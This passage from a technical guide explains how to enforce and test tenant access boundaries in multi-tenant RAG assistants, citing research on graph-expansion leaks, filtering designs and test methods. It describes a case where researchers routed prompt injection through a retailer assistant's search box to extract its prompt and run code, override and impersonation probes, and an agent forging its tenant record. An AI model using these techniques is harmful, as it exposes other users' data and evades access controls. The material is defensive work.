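For tools, the check belongs in ordinary code that runs before the text goes to the model. *Confused ChatGPT* (2026) examined apps that exchange text through a model and concluded that a model acting as the checker can only make a successful attack less likely, because it is itself open to prompt injection. In the example, the file tool is safe because it uses Ana's login, but the preview service has an administrator's access and will open Birch's contract for anyone who pastes the link. Security engineers call such a program a confused deputy because someone with less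 access can get it to use its broad access for them.

Search boxes are easy to overlook because they are often older than the assistant. SecurityInfoWatch's *Retailer's AI Shopping Assistant Found Vulnerable to Five-Stage Exploit Chain* describes a 2026 case in which Rein Security researchers got around a filter meant to keep a large retailer's assistant on the topic of shopping. The filter was weaker in the app's standard search field than in the chat, so they sent their instructions through the search field. They got the system to disclose parts of its internal prompt and information about its tools, and the researchers say they eventually ran their own code in its backend.

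Rein found the flaws on 12 March 2026 and told the retailer the next day. The retailer had not fixed them when Rein published its report on 16 July. Rein withheld the retailer's name for legal reasons, so Rein's account is the only evidence. A permission check that the developers attached only to the chat would have the same weakness as the topic filter, which would not count as an enforcement point for Ana's rule in any case.

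### From a permitted chunk to another tenant's documents

Graph expansion is the best-measured gap in the table. A knowledge graph stores entities such as people and companies as nodes, and links each one to the chunks that mention it. Some pipelines start with a vector search and then follow these links to find related text. Suppose Ana's search returns a chunk of Alder's haulage contract, which she may read. The chunk mentions the haulier, and the haulier's node also links to Birch's contract, so in two steps the pipeline reaches a chunk she may not read.

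Thornton (2026), in *Retrieval Pivot Attacks in Hybrid RAG*, measured how often this happens. Let *S*ₖ(*q*) be the set of items in the context for question *q*, where *k* refers to the size of that set. An item is forbidden to user *u* if it belongs to another tenant or if its sensitivity is above the user's clearance. Retrieval Pivot Risk (RPR) is the probability that a question brings in at least one forbidden item:

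RPR(*u*) = Pr[at least one item in *S*ₖ(*q*) is forbidden to *u*],

with *q* drawn from a set of test questions. Measured on those questions, it is Nouyep and colleagues' query violation rate, calculated on the finished context. Leakage@k counts the forbidden items for one question:

Leakage@k(*q*, *u*) = |{*x* in *S*ₖ(*q*) : *x* is forbidden to *u*}|.

A context with one forbidden item affects RPR as much as a context with twenty, but their Leakage@k differs twentyfold. Entity nodes such as the haulier's don't count towards leakage between tenants, because they belong to no tenant.

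Thornton used three document collections. The first was a synthetic set of 1,000 documents belonging to four organisations that shared some suppliers, staff and computer systems. The second was 50,000 emails from the energy company Enron, with each of five departments treated as a tenant. The third was 887 sections of annual reports that 20 US companies filed with the securities regulator, with each of four industries treated as a tenant.

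| Collection | RPR, vector search alone | RPR, with graph expansion | Mean Leakage@k, with graph expansion | RPR, with a check on every node |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Synthetic documents | 0 | 0.954 | 16.0 | 0 |
| Enron emails | 0 | 0.695 | 7.1 | 0 |
| Annual reports | 0 | 0.085 | 0.4 | 0 |

The vector search had a tenant filter, and it leaked nothing. Adding the graph to the same search made 334 of 350 ordinary questions leak in the synthetic collection, without any attacker. When Thornton planted documents to steer the search, every attack question leaked, but the number of forbidden items hardly rose because the program was already collecting as many nodes as its limit allowed.

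Removing well-known shared names from the graph would not solve the problem. Thornton rebuilt the synthetic collection with no deliberately shared entities, and RPR was still 0.93. The entity-extraction software had also created nodes for things like dates and sums of money, which linked unrelated documents. A better embedding model made matters slightly worse, raising RPR on ordinary questions from 0.954 to 0.994, because more relevant starting chunks led to more entities.

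Every leak was two steps from the starting chunk, so limiting the expansion to one step stopped them all. A limit of 25 nodes also stopped them all, but a limit of 50 still gave an RPR of about 0.66. The 25-node limit worked only because the expansion ended before it reached another tenant's chunks, so it is not an enforcement point. A smaller or differently connected graph could leak within the same limit.

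The fix that Thornton recommends is to check permission again for every node *v* that the expansion reaches:

allowed(*u*, *v*) = (tenant of *v* = tenant of *u*) and (sensitivity of *v* ≤ clearance of *u*).

This reduced RPR to zero in all three collections with no measurable delay. The zero is nearly guaranteed by definition, since the check removes the same items that the metric counts. The amount of useful text that remained is more informative. In the synthetic collection, the context shrank from 110 items to 56, still far more than the 10 from vector search alone.

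Part of that loss comes from the entity nodes, which have no tenant and so always fail the check. Thornton's program follows all the links before filtering, so Alder chunks on the far side of the haulier's node survive. A program that applied the same check during the expansion would stop at that node and miss those chunks. Thornton suggests labelling each entity with all the tenants whose documents mention it, letting the program pass through, and checking the chunks it reaches, but has not tested this. Filtering afterwards can make the system fail noninterference, because Birch's chunks use up places under the limit, as they do in the post-filtered search.

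The risk figures measure leaks into the context the model receives, not into its answers. This is the right measure under the hostile-model assumption, but it doesn't show how often users of a normal model would see the leaked text. In a smaller test of answers, a score for how much leaked entities appeared reached 0.32 for Claude Sonnet 4.5 on the synthetic collection and 0.08 for GPT-5.2 on the Enron emails. The risk figures are also a poor measure of harm, because any email from another department counted as a leak, even though Thornton labelled 92% of the Enron emails "public".

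The fix also depends on correct labels, but the experiments barely test what happens when labels are wrong. Thornton changed up to 5% of the sensitivity labels at random and still found no leaks, but did not change the tenant labels, which the fix relies on most. In another test, an attacker put the target tenant's name on planted documents, which does not expose the target's own files. Neither test covers the most dangerous error for Ana's rule, in which intake labels Birch's contract as Alder's. Thornton advises that the system should assign the labels, never the person uploading a file.

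### A last check before the model

Mu and colleagues recommend checking every passage again when the code assembles the prompt, which could close several gaps at once. In the example, this second check would block Birch's chunks that came through the graph or the search box, as long as each chunk still carried its owner's label.

Previews and summaries of old conversations often arrive as plain text with no label. The last check must reject this text, or the developers must change the code that produces it to keep its sources' labels. Cached answers need a separate check because they bypass prompt assembly.

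New features can add paths that an existing rule does not cover. For example, Microsoft plans to add a control that keeps sensitive files and emails out of answers from its Cowork feature, with release estimated for January 2027 (Windows Forum, *Microsoft Purview Plans to Exclude Unlabeled Sensitive Files and Emails*, 2026). The provider of Ana's assistant should update the inventory before releasing any feature that reads documents or calls a model.

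## Place the access check in the search and count its cost

The provider can enforce the tenant check on Ana's search in four ways. It can keep a separate index for each firm, or keep one index and apply the check either during the search (pre-filtering) or after it (post-filtering). It can also use row-level security, a database feature that limits which rows of a table each user can read, whatever query the application sends. All four keep Birch's text out of Ana's context if everything works, but they differ in what has to work, what happens if there is a mistake, and what they cost.

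| Design | What must work correctly | What a typical mistake does | Main cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Index per tenant | The code that picks the index | Picking the wrong index opens all of Birch's files to Ana | Memory for every index, and copies of shared documents |
| Pre-filtering | The search engine's filter, and the code that passes it Ana's tenant | A search without the condition returns Birch's text and no error | Slower or less complete searches with some types of index |
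| Post-filtering | The application's own filter | Code that reads the results before the filter runs gets Birch's text | Missed results when Alder owns a small share of the store |
| Row-level security | The database, its access policy and the setting that tells it who is asking | A forgotten condition does no harm, but a wrong setting shows Ana another tenant's rows | Slow queries for users with several tenants, and careful handling of connections |

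All four also depend on each chunk getting the right owner at intake. Liu and colleagues concluded from the access-blocking studies in their survey that late checks are much riskier than early ones. They also found that checks on stored labels work better than checks that infer permission from the text. In one study they cite, an AI-driven role filter called ARBITER scored 0.89 on F1, a measure that penalises both wrong refusals and wrong approvals. A simple static filter scored 0.93 to 0.94.

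### Search with and without a gate

Arceo and Narsing, who work at Red Hat, tested an access check in OGX, an open-source framework for RAG and agents. They created three synthetic tenants (finance, engineering and legal) with 100 documents each and some overlap in topics. They compared four configurations, running the search with and without the check, which they call a gate, and running the orchestration in the client's software and on the server. Orchestration is the loop in which the model requests a search, receives the results and continues.

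Each configuration received 300 cross-tenant probes, such as a finance user's request for engineering documents. It also received 90 prompt injection probes, some of which told the system to override its instructions or impersonated someone with a different role.

| Orchestration | Gate | Cross-tenant probes that leaked | Injection probes that leaked |
|---|---|---|---|
| Client | No | 98–100% | 72 of 90 |
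| Server | No | 98–100% | 56 of 90 |
| Client | Yes | 0% | 0 of 90 |
| Server | Yes | 0% | 0 of 90 |

A cross-tenant probe counted as a leak if it returned at least one chunk the user was not allowed to read. Without the gate, injection probes leaked less often than plain questions. Arceo and Narsing explain that the injection probes retrieved other tenants' text through ordinary relevance ranking, so these leak rates are weak evidence of how well the model resists injection. With the gate, the wording of the question made no difference.

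The guarantee depends on four assumptions. The first three are that the login service maps each user to the right tenant, the ownership labels do not change after intake, and the search engine applies its filters correctly. A provider has to check these three on its own system. The experiment could not test the login assumption because a mock service supplied the identities. The fourth, the hostile-model assumption, is that the model may leak anything in its context, which makes the guarantee stronger.

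The gate added about 19 milliseconds to a search. Contacting the login service took 14 of those, and evaluating the policy took less than one. Users would not notice the delay, because the model took 3 to 7 seconds to answer. With 25 simultaneous requests, the client-side system's throughput fell from 5.4 queries per second without the gate to 4.2 with it, although Arceo and Narsing say that the gate does not reduce throughput. The server-side system's throughput rose slightly, from 2.2 to 2.6.

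### Why a gate run by the client is weaker

The two gated systems had the same score because the test client always called the gated search. If Alder runs its own program to search the provider's store, build the prompt and call the model, an attacker who controls that program can call an ungated search instead. The system then behaves like the ungated one in the first row. In Anderson's terms, it does not always invoke the check. With server-side orchestration, the server runs the search and the client chooses only the question.

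The weakness exists only if the client can reach an ungated search. If the server applied the gate to every search request, a hostile client could not retrieve Birch's chunks even while running its own loop. A tester should therefore use Ana's login to send requests directly to every search interface, as well as through the normal application. In this experiment, moving the loop to the server raised the median response time with the gate from 3.4 to 6.4 seconds, mostly because of an extra round trip for the search tool.

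The model can also act as an untrusted client if it chooses the tenant. *The Stochastic Deputy* (Baig, Gillani and colleagues, 2026) reports 373 trials with eight model configurations. In one arm, the model filled in a tenant field and the server checked that the user was entitled to that tenant. Users with access to several tenants passed this check for all of them, so the server fulfilled all 26 requests for a tenant outside the current task.

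With the field removed, the agent could not name another tenant in a tool call. But in 12 of 56 trials it got around this by forging the record of which tenants it could use, because that record was stored where the agent could write to it. The record of a user's tenants therefore needs the same protection as the login.

### How a mixed store crowds out permitted results

Post-filtering can keep every forbidden chunk out of the context and still make the assistant useless. Arceo and Narsing measured this with sqlite-vec, a search engine that cannot apply the tenant condition during the search. Their code fetched five times as many candidates as it needed, then removed the forbidden ones. Recall@5 is the share of the correct top-five results that the system returns.

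| Chunks in the store | Recall@5 | Time added by the filter |
|---|---|---|
| 100 | 1.000 | 0.74 ms |
| 1,000 | 0.100 | 0.79 ms |
| 10,000 | 0.010 | 1.00 ms |
| 50,000 | 0.002 | 2.95 ms |

The filter stayed fast and leaked nothing, but at 50,000 chunks the system returned only one in 500 of the results it should have found. To see why, suppose the search fetches *M* candidates to fill *k* places, and Ana may read a share *σ* of the chunks near her question. On average, *M* × *σ* candidates survive the filter. This limits the average recall:

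recall ≤ min(1, *Mσ* / *k*).

*Recall-Bounded Staleness for Filtered Multi-Tenant ANN Graph Indexes under Concurrent Updates* (Das, Devadkar and Godbole, 2026) derives this limit and a more exact version.

Here *M* is 25 and *k* is 5. Suppose Alder owns 20 chunks. In a store of 100, *σ* is 0.2, so about five candidates survive, which is just enough. In a store of 50,000, *σ* is 0.0004, so 0.01 candidates survive on average, or one for every hundred questions. The limit is then 0.01 / 5 = 0.002. Assuming 20 chunks per tenant reproduces all four recall figures in the table, although Arceo and Narsing do not say how they divided the chunks among tenants. If Alder's share had grown with the store, its recall would not have fallen this way.

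Das and colleagues measured the same effect on 10,000 image vectors, fetching 75 candidates to return ten results. With the tenants' vectors scattered evenly, recall was 95.4% for 6 tenants, 31.4% for 24 and 7.8% for 96. When each tenant's vectors formed clusters, recall was 97.8%, 73.6% and 29.2%. Clustering helps because fewer of the other tenants' vectors lie near the question and take up places among the candidates. Alder and Birch would benefit less on haulage questions, because both firms' haulage contracts lie in the same region.

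The obvious remedy is to fetch more candidates. Das and colleagues calculate that, when a tenant's vectors are evenly scattered, 95% recall requires about 1.25*k*/*σ* candidates, where *k* is the number of results and *σ* is the tenant's share of the store. For ten results and a tenant with 1% of the store, that is 1,250 candidates, which would take about 275 milliseconds on their disk-based index.

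In *Bounded Provisional Visibility*, Xu, Zhou and colleagues (2026) give a test for whether a system over-fetches enough. If the system fetches *α* times as many candidates as it needs, it returns too few results whenever more than 1 − 1/*α* of the candidates are forbidden. Fetching twice as many is enough if up to half are forbidden, and fetching four times as many is enough if up to three-quarters are.

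In their experiment, 30% of all items were hidden. When the system fetched twice as many candidates as it needed, 0.7% of queries returned too few permitted items if the hidden items were spread evenly, 8% if they were clustered by topic and 26% if the researchers chose them to match the queries. Fetching four times as many removed the shortfall in all three cases. Over-fetching therefore suits a firm whose staff are allowed to read most of its files, but a service with 100 equal tenants would have to fetch at least 100 times as many candidates as it needs.

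Filtering before the search avoids the problem because forbidden chunks do not take up places in the results. *CHSR-RRF* (2026) compared filtering before and after the search in an educational assistant that had to stay within a curriculum. Post-filtering had a recall of zero, while pre-filtering filled all eight places with permitted material and found some of the right passages.

### What pre-filtering and separate indexes cost

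Arceo and Narsing recommend engines that filter during the search and say these keep recall at 1.000 whatever the size of the store. Whether recall stays that high depends on the index. Large stores often use a graph index, which links each chunk to its nearest neighbours. A search follows these links towards the question and examines only a small part of the store. If it can pass only through permitted chunks, it may reach a dead end before finding the best ones.

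In *Don't Stir the Pot! Authorized Vector Data Retrieval via Access-Aware Indexing*, Han, Chakraborty and Mehrotra (2026) tested two versions of ACORN, which filters results during a graph search. On a million image vectors, the lighter version found fewer than 40% of the correct results, while the other, which stores more links for each item, found 94% to 97%. A provider that chooses pre-filtering still has to measure recall separately for each tenant, especially the small ones.

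Separate indexes don't have this problem. They found nearly all the right results in Das and colleagues' tests, but memory use grew from 393 MB with 6 tenants to 6,144 MB with 96, although the total number of vectors stayed the same. The test machine had only 3 GB. Rebuilding an index also took that tenant's search offline, for about a quarter of a second with 1,800 vectors and 28 seconds with 100,000.

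The provider can still share other parts of the system among tenants. *Succeeding at Scale* (2026) describes a system in which each tenant has a separate index but all tenants share one embedding model. Each tenant adds a small adapter to that model for its own questions. Arceo and Narsing also share the answering model among tenants, because the gate controls what enters the model's context. For just two firms like Alder and Birch, separate indexes would be affordable and easy to check.

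### One database for text, embeddings and permissions

Many RAG systems keep embeddings in a specialised vector database and store owners, dates and permissions elsewhere. *Beyond Similarity Search* (Budigi and Sirigiri, 2026) proposes putting all of these in PostgreSQL, a general-purpose database, with an extension for vector search. A single query can then retrieve the nearest chunks that belong to Ana's tenant, are recent enough and list her as a permitted reader.

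They compared this with a split design, using 50,000 documents and 20 tenants. They simulated the split with separate PostgreSQL tables, whose results application code had to merge, and did not use an actual vector database. These are the median times:

| Conditions on the search | Split design | Single database |
|---|---|---|
| Similarity only | 0.92 ms | 0.91 ms |
| Similarity and date | 9.63 ms | 0.75 ms |
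| Similarity, tenant and category | 1.77 ms | 0.46 ms |
| All conditions | 0.43 ms | 0.25 ms |

The single database was faster whenever the query had extra conditions. But Budigi and Sirigiri do not report recall, and a query can be fast because it returns too few results. Even when the query includes the tenant condition, the database may search the vector index first and then drop the other tenants' rows. In that case it is post-filtering internally and can miss results in the same way.

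The split design leaked in two of 1,000 queries, and the single database leaked in none. The leaks came from simulated bugs in the application's filter, so the rate depends on how the researchers set up those bugs and doesn't estimate how often real systems leak. The query that Budigi and Sirigiri print contains an ordinary condition that a developer could leave out, although they say the database makes such leaks impossible. Real row-level security would add the condition even if the developer forgot it.

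Their stronger argument is about stale permissions. If the provider updates the permission records and the copy in the vector database separately, a search between the two updates may use the old permission. Budigi and Sirigiri measured an average gap of 3.54 milliseconds between updating a document's metadata and updating its embedding. A single database can make both changes in one transaction, so no search uses one without the other.

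Gaps in deployed systems can be much longer than this. Xu, Zhou and colleagues hid items in Milvus, a vector database, and kept searching for them. Under its two looser consistency settings, the items remained retrievable for a median of about 0.3 seconds. Under the two stricter settings, no completed search returned them. In RoyChowdhury and colleagues' tests of Copilot, a full product, deleted text remained available much longer, for about three minutes.

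A single database does not remove the delay if the permissions come from another system, such as Birch's file server. The provider still has to copy each change into the database, and the 15-minute limit in the sample specification also covers that step. For collections of hundreds of millions of documents, Budigi and Sirigiri themselves recommend moving older files to a specialised vector database, which brings back the second copy.

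### Row-level security in practice

Baig and colleagues compared enforcement in the database with enforcement in application code on a commercial property-management system that uses MySQL. For the database version, they built views (saved queries) that included the tenant condition. The application's account could read the views but not the underlying tables. A query written to bypass the condition returned an error.

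In the other version, all queries had to go through one application module, which added the condition. Forgetting to use the module's query builder caused a crash instead of a silent leak. But the application's account could still read every table, so any code that opened its own connection could see every tenant's data. The live system used this weaker version because changing the production database required approval. The researchers tried the views only on a local copy.

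Database enforcement can fail when an application reuses connections to save time. If Ben's request leaves the tenant set to "Birch" on a connection that Ana's request then uses, the database will apply the wrong rule, and nothing in the log will look unusual. Baig and colleagues avoided this by opening a new connection for every request. Opening one took 638 milliseconds, about 21 times as long as a typical query, although their route included a virtual private network. They now think it would be better to reuse connections and reset the tenant each time, but they have not built this.

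A policy also has to cover every table a query reads. In the property system, a correctly filtered booking could link to a customer record that another tenant had created. This happened in 15.72% of rows for the worst-affected link. A RAG store would have the same fault if it filtered the chunks but not a linked table of document titles and authors.

The check can be slow for users with access to several tenants. A common test for whether a row belongs to any tenant on a list prevents the database from using its index efficiently. On one large table, this test took 5.8 seconds, compared with 0.1 seconds when it was rewritten as a join between the table and the list. Even when the policy works, response times may reveal something about hidden rows.

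### Indexes organised by permission

Storage becomes a bigger problem within a firm, where people in different roles share many documents. If Alder's managers, accountants and dispatchers each had their own index, a contract that all three groups could read would be stored three times. Han and colleagues calculated that, for three datasets with 64 to 87 roles, one index per role would need 5.3 to 15.1 times as much storage as a single copy of the data.

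Their method, VEDA, looks for a compromise within a storage limit. It first sorts chunks into blocks according to exactly which roles may read them. It can then copy a block into a group that only some of those roles search, which uses extra storage but adds no forbidden chunks to their searches. Or it can merge blocks with different permissions, which takes no extra storage but makes some roles search through chunks they may not read.

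For a role *r* and a group *G*, the cost of mixing depends on

*λ* = (chunks in *G*) / (chunks in *G* that *r* may read),

rounded up. If accountants can read 1,000 of a group's 5,000 chunks, *λ* is 5 and a full search has to consider five times as many candidates. VEDA searches the fully permitted groups first. It then tries a normal search of each mixed group and widens it only if the group might still contain something closer than the results already found.

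With about 10% extra storage, VEDA handled on average 2.2 to 5.6 times as many queries per second as SIEVE and 8.7 to 42.6 times as many as HoneyBee, two earlier methods that also divide the data into several indexes. On the image dataset, its recall was at least 99%. Han and colleagues generated the access rules from a benchmark of organisational roles, so the savings in a real firm would depend on how much its roles overlap. They also tested their own method, as did the researchers behind the other designs compared here. Liu and colleagues found some concern about independent evaluation in 109 of the 118 RAG defence papers they reviewed, largely because researchers had tested their own methods.

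VEDA's security also depends on how the index groups chunks. VEDA filters results from mixed groups but relies on the other groups containing only permitted chunks. If accountants lose access to a contract and the groups aren't updated, a search may still return it to them without a check. Han and colleagues leave efficient updates after such changes to future work. Until then, the application can check each of the few final chunks against the current permission table before it builds the prompt. This check removes only chunks whose permissions have changed since the index was last updated, so it avoids the large loss of recall caused by post-filtering a mixed store.

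## Test the boundary without relying on the model's good behaviour

A model may refuse to reveal Birch's pallet rate even when the rate is in its context. Seven tests give better evidence than a refusal, mostly by checking what the code retrieves and passes to the model rather than how the model replies.

The tests need a copy of the system that logs every context given to the model. The tester plants canaries, which are unique harmless strings such as `heron-4471-quill`, in documents that the test user may not read. If a canary reaches the user, text from that document has leaked. Some tests replace the model with a stub, a simple program that returns its whole context as the answer.

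| Test | Input | Passes if | A failure means |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Check the context | Ana's questions, with each context stopped just before the model receives it | Every recipient may read every passage | The path that supplied the passage has no working check |
| 2. Print the context | The same questions, with the stub as the model | No canary reaches Ana | Forbidden text got through, perhaps with a wrong or missing label |
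| 3. Delete the security sentences | The same questions and the real model, with a shortened prompt | The result is the same as before: no Birch text in any answer | The rule depended on the prompt |
| 4. Change the forbidden documents | Two stores that differ only in Birch's files | Contexts are identical, and answers differ no more than chance allows | Birch's files affect what Ana sees |
| 5. Generate random cases | Random users, groups, permissions and questions | The search agrees with a simple, separate model of the permissions | The code breaks the rules in a case nobody thought of, or the model is wrong |
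| 6. Withdraw access | A document that Ana may read until the tester withdraws permission | No context contains it after the 15-minute limit | A copy of the text or of the permissions is out of date |
| 7. Remove each check | The system with one check disabled at a time | At least one of the other tests now fails | Nothing was testing that check |

Suppose the provider has closed the five gaps in its inventory by giving each path its own permission check, and has added a final check on the finished context. The tester loads 400 documents from each firm, plants a different canary in each of 40 Birch documents, and writes 120 questions, three on the subject of each of those 40 documents. These figures and all later results for Alder and Birch are invented.

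### Check the context, then print it

In test 1, a few lines of code run after the prompt is assembled and check every passage against the owner's permission records. The code should not use the copy of the permissions in the search index, because if that copy is wrong, the test would repeat the system's mistake and pass.

*A Policy Algebra for Trust-Preserving Agentic AI Execution* (2026) sketches a similar test. A finance user searches for salary data in a collection whose only document is a restricted personnel file. The test passes only if the file is missing from the results and the audit log records a refusal. Without the second condition, the test would also pass if the search crashed or the index never loaded. A pre-filter never considers the forbidden document, so it may have no refusal to log. For Ana's rule, the tester can instead have Ben of Birch ask the same question and confirm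 that he receives the passage. The sketched test checks only the search results, while test 1 must also cover anything that other paths add later.

Test 1 relies on labels, so if intake has filed a Birch contract under Alder, the lookup approves it. Test 2 instead searches everything Ana receives for the 40 canaries. The tester first replaces every model that writes text with the stub, including any that rewrites questions or summarises old conversations. Summaries need the stub because a real model would probably drop an odd string like a canary and keep the pallet rate. To cover the answer cache, Ben asks each question first and Ana repeats it.

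Code that runs after the model can hide a leak from this test. An output filter might delete strange strings, or a length limit might cut off a long answer. The tester should search the stub's raw output as well as Ana's screen. If the model normally chooses its own searches, the stub also needs to run a script of hostile requests, such as asking for Birch's tenant in every field that accepts a tenant, and then print the results.

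In the example, test 1 passes on all 120 questions, but test 2 finds one canary. The document came from a mailbox that both firms use for the joint bid. Intake labelled everything in that mailbox as Alder's, so every permission check worked correctly but used the wrong label.

### Delete the security sentences

The stub ignores instructions, so test 3 needs the real model. The tester removes "Never reveal anything from Birch's files" and any similar sentence from the system prompt, asks the questions again, and searches the answers for canaries and known facts such as Birch's rate. If these appear only after the deletion, those instructions had been keeping them out of the answers.

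A failure in test 3 is conclusive, but a pass is weaker evidence than a pass in test 2, because the model might have had the rate in its context and left it out of the answer. The test is most useful when the tester can edit the prompt but not replace the model, as with many hosted assistants.

*Revoked but Still Authoritative* (2026) similarly measured how often AI agents took unsafe actions because they relied on revoked facts in their memory. With no defence, this happened in 43.1% of cases. Instructions to disregard superseded facts lowered the rate only to 37.2%, because nothing in the context showed which facts were superseded. An output filter lowered it only to 18.1%, even though the filter had the text of the revoked facts. A filter on the memory store lowered it to zero in 1,620 cases, and the result was the same with or without the instructions, as it should be for an enforced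 rule.

Mușetoiu (2026), in *RAGAL*, describes what was in effect an accidental version of test 3. RAGAL is an assistant for technical-support staff at a Romanian government agency, and it runs on the agency's own machines. Its prompt began with about 2,000 tokens of rules. Nobody had set the size of the context window, so the server used its default of about 4,000 tokens and cut the beginning off longer prompts without any error message. For weeks, the model often worked without its rules. It ignored restrictions and once answered in the wrong language, which the team blamed on the model's small size. One restriction was enforced by a program that intercepted requests for live data before they reached the model. The system still passed the tests of that restriction in evaluations run while the prompts were being cut.

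### Change only the forbidden documents

Ordinary testing is difficult here because nobody can write down the correct answer to every question Ana might ask. *Metamorphic Testing* (Chen, Cheung and Yiu, 1998) proposes running a program twice on related inputs and checking a relation that must hold between the two results. One of its examples is a program that finds the shortest path between two points in a large network, where checking the answer directly is impractical. If every link works in both directions, the distance from *x* to *y* must equal the distance from *y* to *x*. If the program gives two different distances, the tester knows it has a fault without knowing the correct distance.

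Test 4 applies this method to the specification's second rule, using pairs of stores that differ only in Birch's files. In one pair, the tester deletes Birch's files from the second store to check whether they take up places in the search results. In another, the tester changes Birch's pallet rate but keeps the same number of files, to check whether their content has an effect.

The tester can compare contexts character by character after removing timestamps and request numbers. It helps to compare two identical stores first, because building some vector indexes involves randomness, which alone can make the contexts differ. Fixing the random seed solves this. Using exact search for the test would too, but it would hide any effect that Birch's embeddings have on the index Ana really uses.

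In the example, two identical stores give the same 120 contexts. Deleting Birch's files from one of them changes seven of its contexts. Each of the seven contains the same Alder passages as before, in a different order. The order changed because the keyword search gives rare words more weight, and it measured rarity across both firms' files. Tests 1 and 2 could not have found this, because no Birch text is in any of the contexts.

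Answers need a statistical comparison. Even with the model's randomness turned off and a fixed seed, Mușetoiu found, calculations on graphics processors do not come out exactly the same each time. Suppose the tester asks one question *n* = 200 times on each store, and the assistant refuses 24 times with Birch's files present and 46 times without them. The two refusal rates are *p*₁ = 0.12 and *p*₂ = 0.23, and the overall rate is *p* = 0.175. The difference in standard errors is

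*z* = |*p*₁ − *p*₂| / √(2*p*(1 − *p*)/*n*) = 0.11 / 0.038 ≈ 2.9.

Chance produces a gap this large in about four of every 1,000 comparisons, so a tester who compares several features of the answers to many questions will occasionally see one. Here the tester repeats the question 200 times on each store and gets 31 and 34 refusals, so the first gap was probably chance. If the contexts are identical but a difference in the answers keeps recurring, the model is getting information that isn't in the context log.

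Kim, Pasini and Tonella (2026), in *When Knowledge Changes*, used metamorphic testing to measure how reliable RAG answers are when documents change. They made 28,500 altered versions of test cases from five datasets, for instance by adding off-topic sentences, which should leave the answer the same, or a contradictory fact, which should change it. The system's answers violated these expectations in 4.9% to 10.2% of cases, depending on the dataset and on whether the stored documents or the retrieved text had been altered. When off-topic sentences were added to the stored documents, the answer changed in 2.9% to 11.4% of cases. Answers can therefore change for reasons unrelated to access, so the comparison of contexts should come first.

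### Compare the search with a simple model of the permissions

Handwritten tests cover the situations their author thought of. Arceo and Narsing, for example, checked their access rules against a table of 48 cases and got every one right. Property-based testing covers many more by generating cases at random. *QuickCheck* (Claessen and Hughes, 2000) introduced a tool that does this for Haskell programs. The programmer states a general property, such as "reversing a list twice gives the original list", and the tool tries it on 100 random inputs and reports any that break it. It starts with small inputs, so the first counterexample is often easy to understand.

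For test 5, the generator creates a few tenants, users, groups and documents, assigns permissions at random and makes up a question. A separate function decides what each user may read:

may(*u*, *d*) = (*u* and *d* have the same tenant and share a group) or (*u* is on *d*'s guest list).

The function can be slow, since it only has to handle a few dozen documents. The test checks that the search returns no documents the function forbids and that it returns the best-matching documents the function allows. Without the second check, a search that always returned nothing would pass. Someone who has not read the search code should write the function from the agreed rules, so that the two don't share a mistake.

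Random cases can be too easy. When Claessen and Hughes tested a property of inserting an item into a sorted list, it passed all 100 cases, but the list was empty in 43% of them. In another run, only 19 lists had more than one element. In the example, 1,180 of the first 2,000 cases likewise contain no forbidden document that resembles the question, so a search with no filter would pass them. The tester changes the generator to copy each question from a forbidden document, and soon finds a case where a user who belongs to no groups receives another tenant's document. The search code turns a user's groups into a condition, but leaves the condition out when the user has none.

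Baig and colleagues test for the same kind of fault in their property-management system. They check that a user with no tenants gets the condition `1 = 0`, which no row satisfies, rather than no condition. Their 228 assertions also include a check, on every run, that the tables and columns in the live database match the assumptions in the access code. This check exposed three previously unnoticed wrong settings that random tests on a scratch database would not have found.

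Language models can also write property-based tests. *A Multi-Domain Study on the Effectiveness of LLMs at Writing Property-Based Tests* (2026) describes an earlier tool, Agentic-PBT, in which a coding agent infers properties from Python code and its documentation, tests them and reports failures. Its developers reviewed 50 of the reports that a model had ranked highest and judged 28 to be real bugs, so a person has to review each report. An agent that infers an access rule from the code may also mistake a fault in the code for the rule, so the properties should come from the specification.

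### Withdraw access and time the result

Test 6 starts with a document that contains a canary and that Ana has permission to read. The tester confirms that the canary appears in her context, withdraws her permission, and repeats the question every ten seconds. The tester measures the time from the withdrawal to the canary's last appearance. If several servers answer searches, the passage may disappear from one and return from another a minute later, so the tester should continue past the 15-minute limit.

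A user can lose access to a document in several ways, and different code may handle each one. The owner might remove Ana from the document's access list, remove her from a group, delete the document or close her account. Each of these cases needs its own test, as does each path by which the system can supply the document's text.

The difference between paths can be large. Xu, Zhou and colleagues tried two ways of hiding items in Milvus Lite, a small version of the Milvus database. When they relied on the filter inside the index, 29% to 48% of searches made immediately after the update still returned the hidden item. When the system filtered the results after the search, none did. *Revoked but Still Authoritative* tested the effect of settings by running mem0, a memory system for agents, twice on the same data with one retrieval setting changed. In 39 of 81 matched comparisons, the change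 turned a safe result into an unsafe one, and it never did the reverse. A revocation test is therefore evidence only for the settings it used, so it should use those of the live system.

In the example, the tester withdraws access 20 times. The search stops returning the document four to nine minutes later. But when Ana asks a follow-up question in an old conversation, the passage reappears 52 minutes after the withdrawal. The code that resends old messages checks them against a copy of the permissions that the provider updates once an hour. The final check before text reaches the model relies on the same copy. The provider then changes the code for old messages to look up the current permissions.

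### Remove each check and see whether a test notices

The first six tests could all pass because the system is secure or because the tests are poor. Mutation testing distinguishes the two by introducing faults on purpose. DeMillo, Lipton and Sayward proposed it in a 1978 paper, which *Development and Analysis of Mutation Testing* (Cummings, 2019) summarises. The tester makes many copies of a program, called mutants, each with one small fault, and runs the tests on each. If every test still passes on a mutant, it has "survived" and the tests have a gap. The method relies on the conjecture that tests which catch simple errors also tend to catch complicated ones. *Theoretical and Empirical Studies on Using Program Mutation* (Budd, DeMillo and colleagues, 1980) describes the wider problem that a tester can try only a finite set of inputs but wants correct results on those to be good evidence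 about all the others.

For an access rule, the most useful mutants each have one security check removed. In the example, the provider removes five, one at a time:

| Check removed | Tests that fail (invented) | What the tester sees |
|---|---|---|
| Tenant condition on the vector search | 4 and 5 | Birch's passages appear in the raw results, and Ana's contexts lose Alder passages |
| Permission check in the graph expansion | 4 | Birch's passages use up places, so deleting Birch's files changes the context |
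| Separate cache entries for each firm | 2 | Ana receives an answer stored for Ben, with a canary in it |
| Current permissions for old messages | 6 | A withdrawn passage returns after 52 minutes |
| Last check before the model | None | Nothing changes |

All the existing tests still pass when the last check is removed, because every path now has its own filter, which leaves the last check nothing to remove. The check could have stopped working months ago without any test failing. The provider added it for cases where an earlier filter fails, so the tester has to create such a case. A new test passes a Birch passage directly to the prompt-assembly code and requires the code to reject it. This test fails when the last check is removed.

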